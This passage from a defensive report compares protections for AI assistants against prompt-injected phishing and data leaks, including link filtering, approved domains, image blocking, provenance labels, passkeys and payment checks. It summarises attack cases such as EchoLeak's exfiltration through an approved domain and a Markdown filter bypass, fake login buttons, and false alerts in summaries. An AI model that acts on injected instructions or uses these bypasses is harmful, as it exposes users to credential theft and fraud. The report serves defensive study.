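Removing every link is the safest rule, but it also removes legitimate ones, such as a supplier's order page. Gemini removes only links that look suspicious. It checks them with Google Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying harmful sites, and replaces suspicious ones with the words "suspicious link removed". Users keep most legitimate links, but Gemini may miss a newly registered phishing site.

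Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that Gemini also sent links through a google.com address. This could let Google check a site again when the user clicks, by which time Google may know more about the site. But a user who looks at the address before clicking may see Google's name first and feel reassured.

#### Allowing only approved domains

The application can instead allow links only to a list of approved domains, as Salesforce does for its agents. This blocks a new phishing site without anyone having to recognise it as dangerous. But an attacker can still exploit an approved domain, even if the company keeps the list up to date. In EchoLeak, the zero-click attack on Copilot, the researchers got data out through an approved Microsoft Teams address that fetched content from elsewhere. They also got past a link filter with a less common form of Markdown, in which the address is separate from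 the label.

A list of approved sites also can't filter pages by their content. Criminals have put fake login pages on Google's free website service, for example, so a company that approves all of Google's domains could let one through.

#### Blocking remote images

A remote image can send data to its server as soon as it appears, and it can also contain a QR code. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* says Microsoft dealt with the first problem in Bing Chat in May 2023 by adding a Content-Security-Policy header, which tells the browser which sites a page may load content from. Embrace The Red reported the same problem to OpenAI that year but got little response. Three years later, Permiso could still make ChatGPT load a remote image.

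Blocking these images also removes harmless web pictures from answers. It does not block ordinary links, which Checkmarx points out can carry the same private data.

#### Showing the full address

An application can print the address next to each link so users don't have to hover over it. This keeps every link usable and gives phone users information that is otherwise hard to find. It only helps if users read the address and notice that it is wrong, and attackers can register a domain that looks almost right. Long addresses also clutter the summary, so the application could show the domain in larger type and shorten the rest.

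Displaying untrusted links as text links instead of buttons may help too, as the *It's a TRAP!* tests on web agents suggest.

#### Adding provenance labels

A provenance label such as "From an external email" could show the employee that the assistant didn't write the account notice. The application has to add this label, because a compromised model could leave it out or write a false one.

It is hard to know what to label, because a model can combine three emails in one sentence and the application has no simple way to tell which words came from which. Microsoft's FIDES system draws on *information-flow control*, an established way of tracking where data comes from and where it may go. In the simplest form of this method, anything a program produces from untrusted data also counts as untrusted. This rule would never miss an outsider's text in a summary. But if one of 40 messages came from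 outside, the whole summary would carry the label, and employees who saw it on nearly every summary might soon ignore it.

A more useful design would show any link, phone number or request for action as a direct quotation in a separate box that names the sender. The application can check that the quoted words appear in the email. It could miss a request that the model has rephrased, so the whole summary would still need a general label. Warnings helped only some people in the HAT-Lab experiment, and nobody has tested this design against fake login notices.

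### Sign-in prompts that the model can't imitate

A web page can draw almost anything inside its own area of the browser window, but it can't write in the address bar. An assistant could similarly show real sign-in requests only in a fixed part of the window where the model's text can't appear. Any login button inside an answer would then be fake or at least unnecessary.

This would be slightly less convenient, since users would have to look somewhere else to sign in. It would also depend on their knowing the rule. An attacker could still write "Your session has expired" in the summary, and someone who had never noticed where the real prompt appears might click on the link below. A developer can remove that risk by combining the protected area with strict rules on links. Developers also have to confine the answer to its own area, which would have stopped the fake vLex login screen from appearing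 over the whole chat.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting assistants to outside tools, includes part of this idea. In the November 2025 version, a connected tool that needs a password or payment details must send the user to a web page rather than ask for them in a form in the assistant. The assistant's application must show the full address and get the user's agreement before opening the page, and must open it so that the model can't read what the user types. The standard also advises against making links clickable anywhere else in the request.

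The MCP Apps extension, launched in January 2026, lets tools display interactive components such as forms and charts inside a conversation. The application shows each component in a *sandboxed* frame, which prevents it from reading or changing the rest of the window, but it can still draw a convincing login form inside its own frame.

These rules cover requests and components from connected tools, but not ordinary Markdown links that the model writes in its answer, which the attacks on Copilot and ChatGPT used. A malicious tool could also follow the sign-in rules and still send the user to a real consent page for the attacker's application. Developers of assistants would therefore have to apply similar rules to everything in an answer, which the standard doesn't require.

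### Protection at the organisation

An employer usually can't change the assistant's renderer, but it can limit what an attacker gains from a click.

#### Passkeys

A *passkey* replaces the password with a secret key stored on the user's device or in their password manager. When the user signs in, the website sends a random challenge and the device signs it with the key for that site. The browser checks the site's domain, so the key for the real login page doesn't work on an imitation. The user also has no password to type into the fake page.

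Passkeys would stop the fake login pages that Permiso's Copilot alert or a QR code could lead to, and would protect someone whose assistant gives a wrong login address by mistake. They would also make the false Gemini alert less useful, because the scammer who answers the phone couldn't ask for a password. The scammer might still persuade the victim to install a program that gives control of the computer.

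Passkeys don't help against Logue's button or Radware's leaking file, because those attacks steal data without a login. They don't help against CoPhish either, because the user's passkey would work normally on the real Microsoft site.

Employers also have to help people who lose their devices. If they keep passwords as a backup for this, an attacker can use a fake page to claim that the passkey has failed and ask for the password instead. The protection is complete only when the account no longer accepts a password.

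#### Limits on application consent

An employer can require an administrator to approve any application that wants access to email or files. This would stop CoPhish from getting access through ordinary staff, but not through an administrator who can grant it. Staff have to wait for approval of useful applications, and a busy administrator may approve requests without reading them carefully. The requirement does not protect against a fake login page, because an attacker who obtains a password signs in as the user.

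Employers can also limit what an assistant can read. Microsoft lets organisations label sensitive files and stop Copilot from summarising them. An attacker who takes control of Copilot can then steal less, but employees can't use it to summarise those files, which may be among the longest they have to read.

#### Separate approval of payments

Neither a link rule nor a passkey would stop the false payment details in Barracuda's invoice example. The employer can require a second person to confirm any new bank details by calling the supplier on a number already on file.

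The second employee has to check the details with the supplier, not with the assistant. If both employees read the same AI summary, they will see the same false account number and may take their agreement as confirmation. Calling the supplier delays some payments, but companies only need to do it when bank details change.

### What Google, Microsoft and OpenAI say they do

The three companies describe different combinations of these defences. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) covers the company's strictest option, which users or administrators have to turn on.

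| | Google | Microsoft | OpenAI |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Outside text | Classifiers, and reminders to the model to stick to the user's task | Prompt Shields and Spotlighting | Lockdown Mode uses stored copies of web pages and limits live connections to other services |
| Links | Replaces suspicious addresses with a notice | Blocks certain untrusted links | Checks addresses before ChatGPT opens them |
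| Images | Doesn't display external images | Blocks a known way of leaking data through images | Lockdown Mode restricts images in answers |
| The user's part | Confirms risky actions and gets a notice about blocked attacks | Approves some actions, such as sending a drafted email | Sees "Elevated Risk" labels on certain features |

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for organisations in February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts in June. The mode also restricts file downloads and Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. OpenAI says most users don't need it. Workplace administrators can choose which connected applications remain available and what ChatGPT may do in them.

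OpenAI says Lockdown Mode is meant to prevent private data from leaving the conversation. Several of its restrictions would also hinder the attacks in this report. Blocking file downloads would keep Radware's fake shop and leaking file from reaching the user, and blocking images in answers would keep out the remote QR code. But OpenAI doesn't list ordinary links among the restricted features, and an attacker can show a false alert with a phone number using only text. A stored copy of a web page can also contain the attacker's instructions.

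The "Elevated Risk" labels warn about a feature, such as internet access for OpenAI's coding assistant. They don't show whether a particular sentence came from a third party, so they can't serve as provenance labels.

Of these measures, Google's link removal most directly targets phishing links in a summary. Microsoft describes its link and image blocking as preventing data theft, and the protection may vary between products. Checkmarx demonstrated a data leak in Copilot Chat that needed no click, and says Microsoft didn't commit to a fix because it didn't consider the leak a vulnerability. None of the three companies describes a measure that would reliably stop a false alert written in plain text.

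### Which defences work against which attacks

The table shows how well the defences work against the main attacks in this report. "Mostly" means the defence blocks the attack apart from the exceptions described above, and "partly" means it makes the attack less likely to succeed. The ratings assume strict rules for links, images and files. They are judgements based on how each defence works, because researchers haven't tested most of these combinations.

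| Attack | Text cleaning and model training | Link, image and file rules | Protected sign-in area | Passkeys | Organisation's approval rules |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Fake login link from hidden instructions | Partly | Mostly | Partly | Mostly | No |
| Fake login link in a visible notice that the assistant repeats | No | Mostly | Partly | Mostly | No |
| QR code that leads to a fake login page | Partly | Mostly | Partly | Mostly | No |
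| False alert with a phone number | Partly | No | No | Partly | No |
| Private data inside a link disguised as a login button | Partly | Mostly | Partly | No | No |
| Downloaded file that leaks private data | Partly | Mostly | No | No | No |
| Consent request from an agent the attacker built | No | No | No | No | Mostly, through consent limits |
| False payment details in a summary | Partly | No | No | No | Mostly, through separate payment approval |
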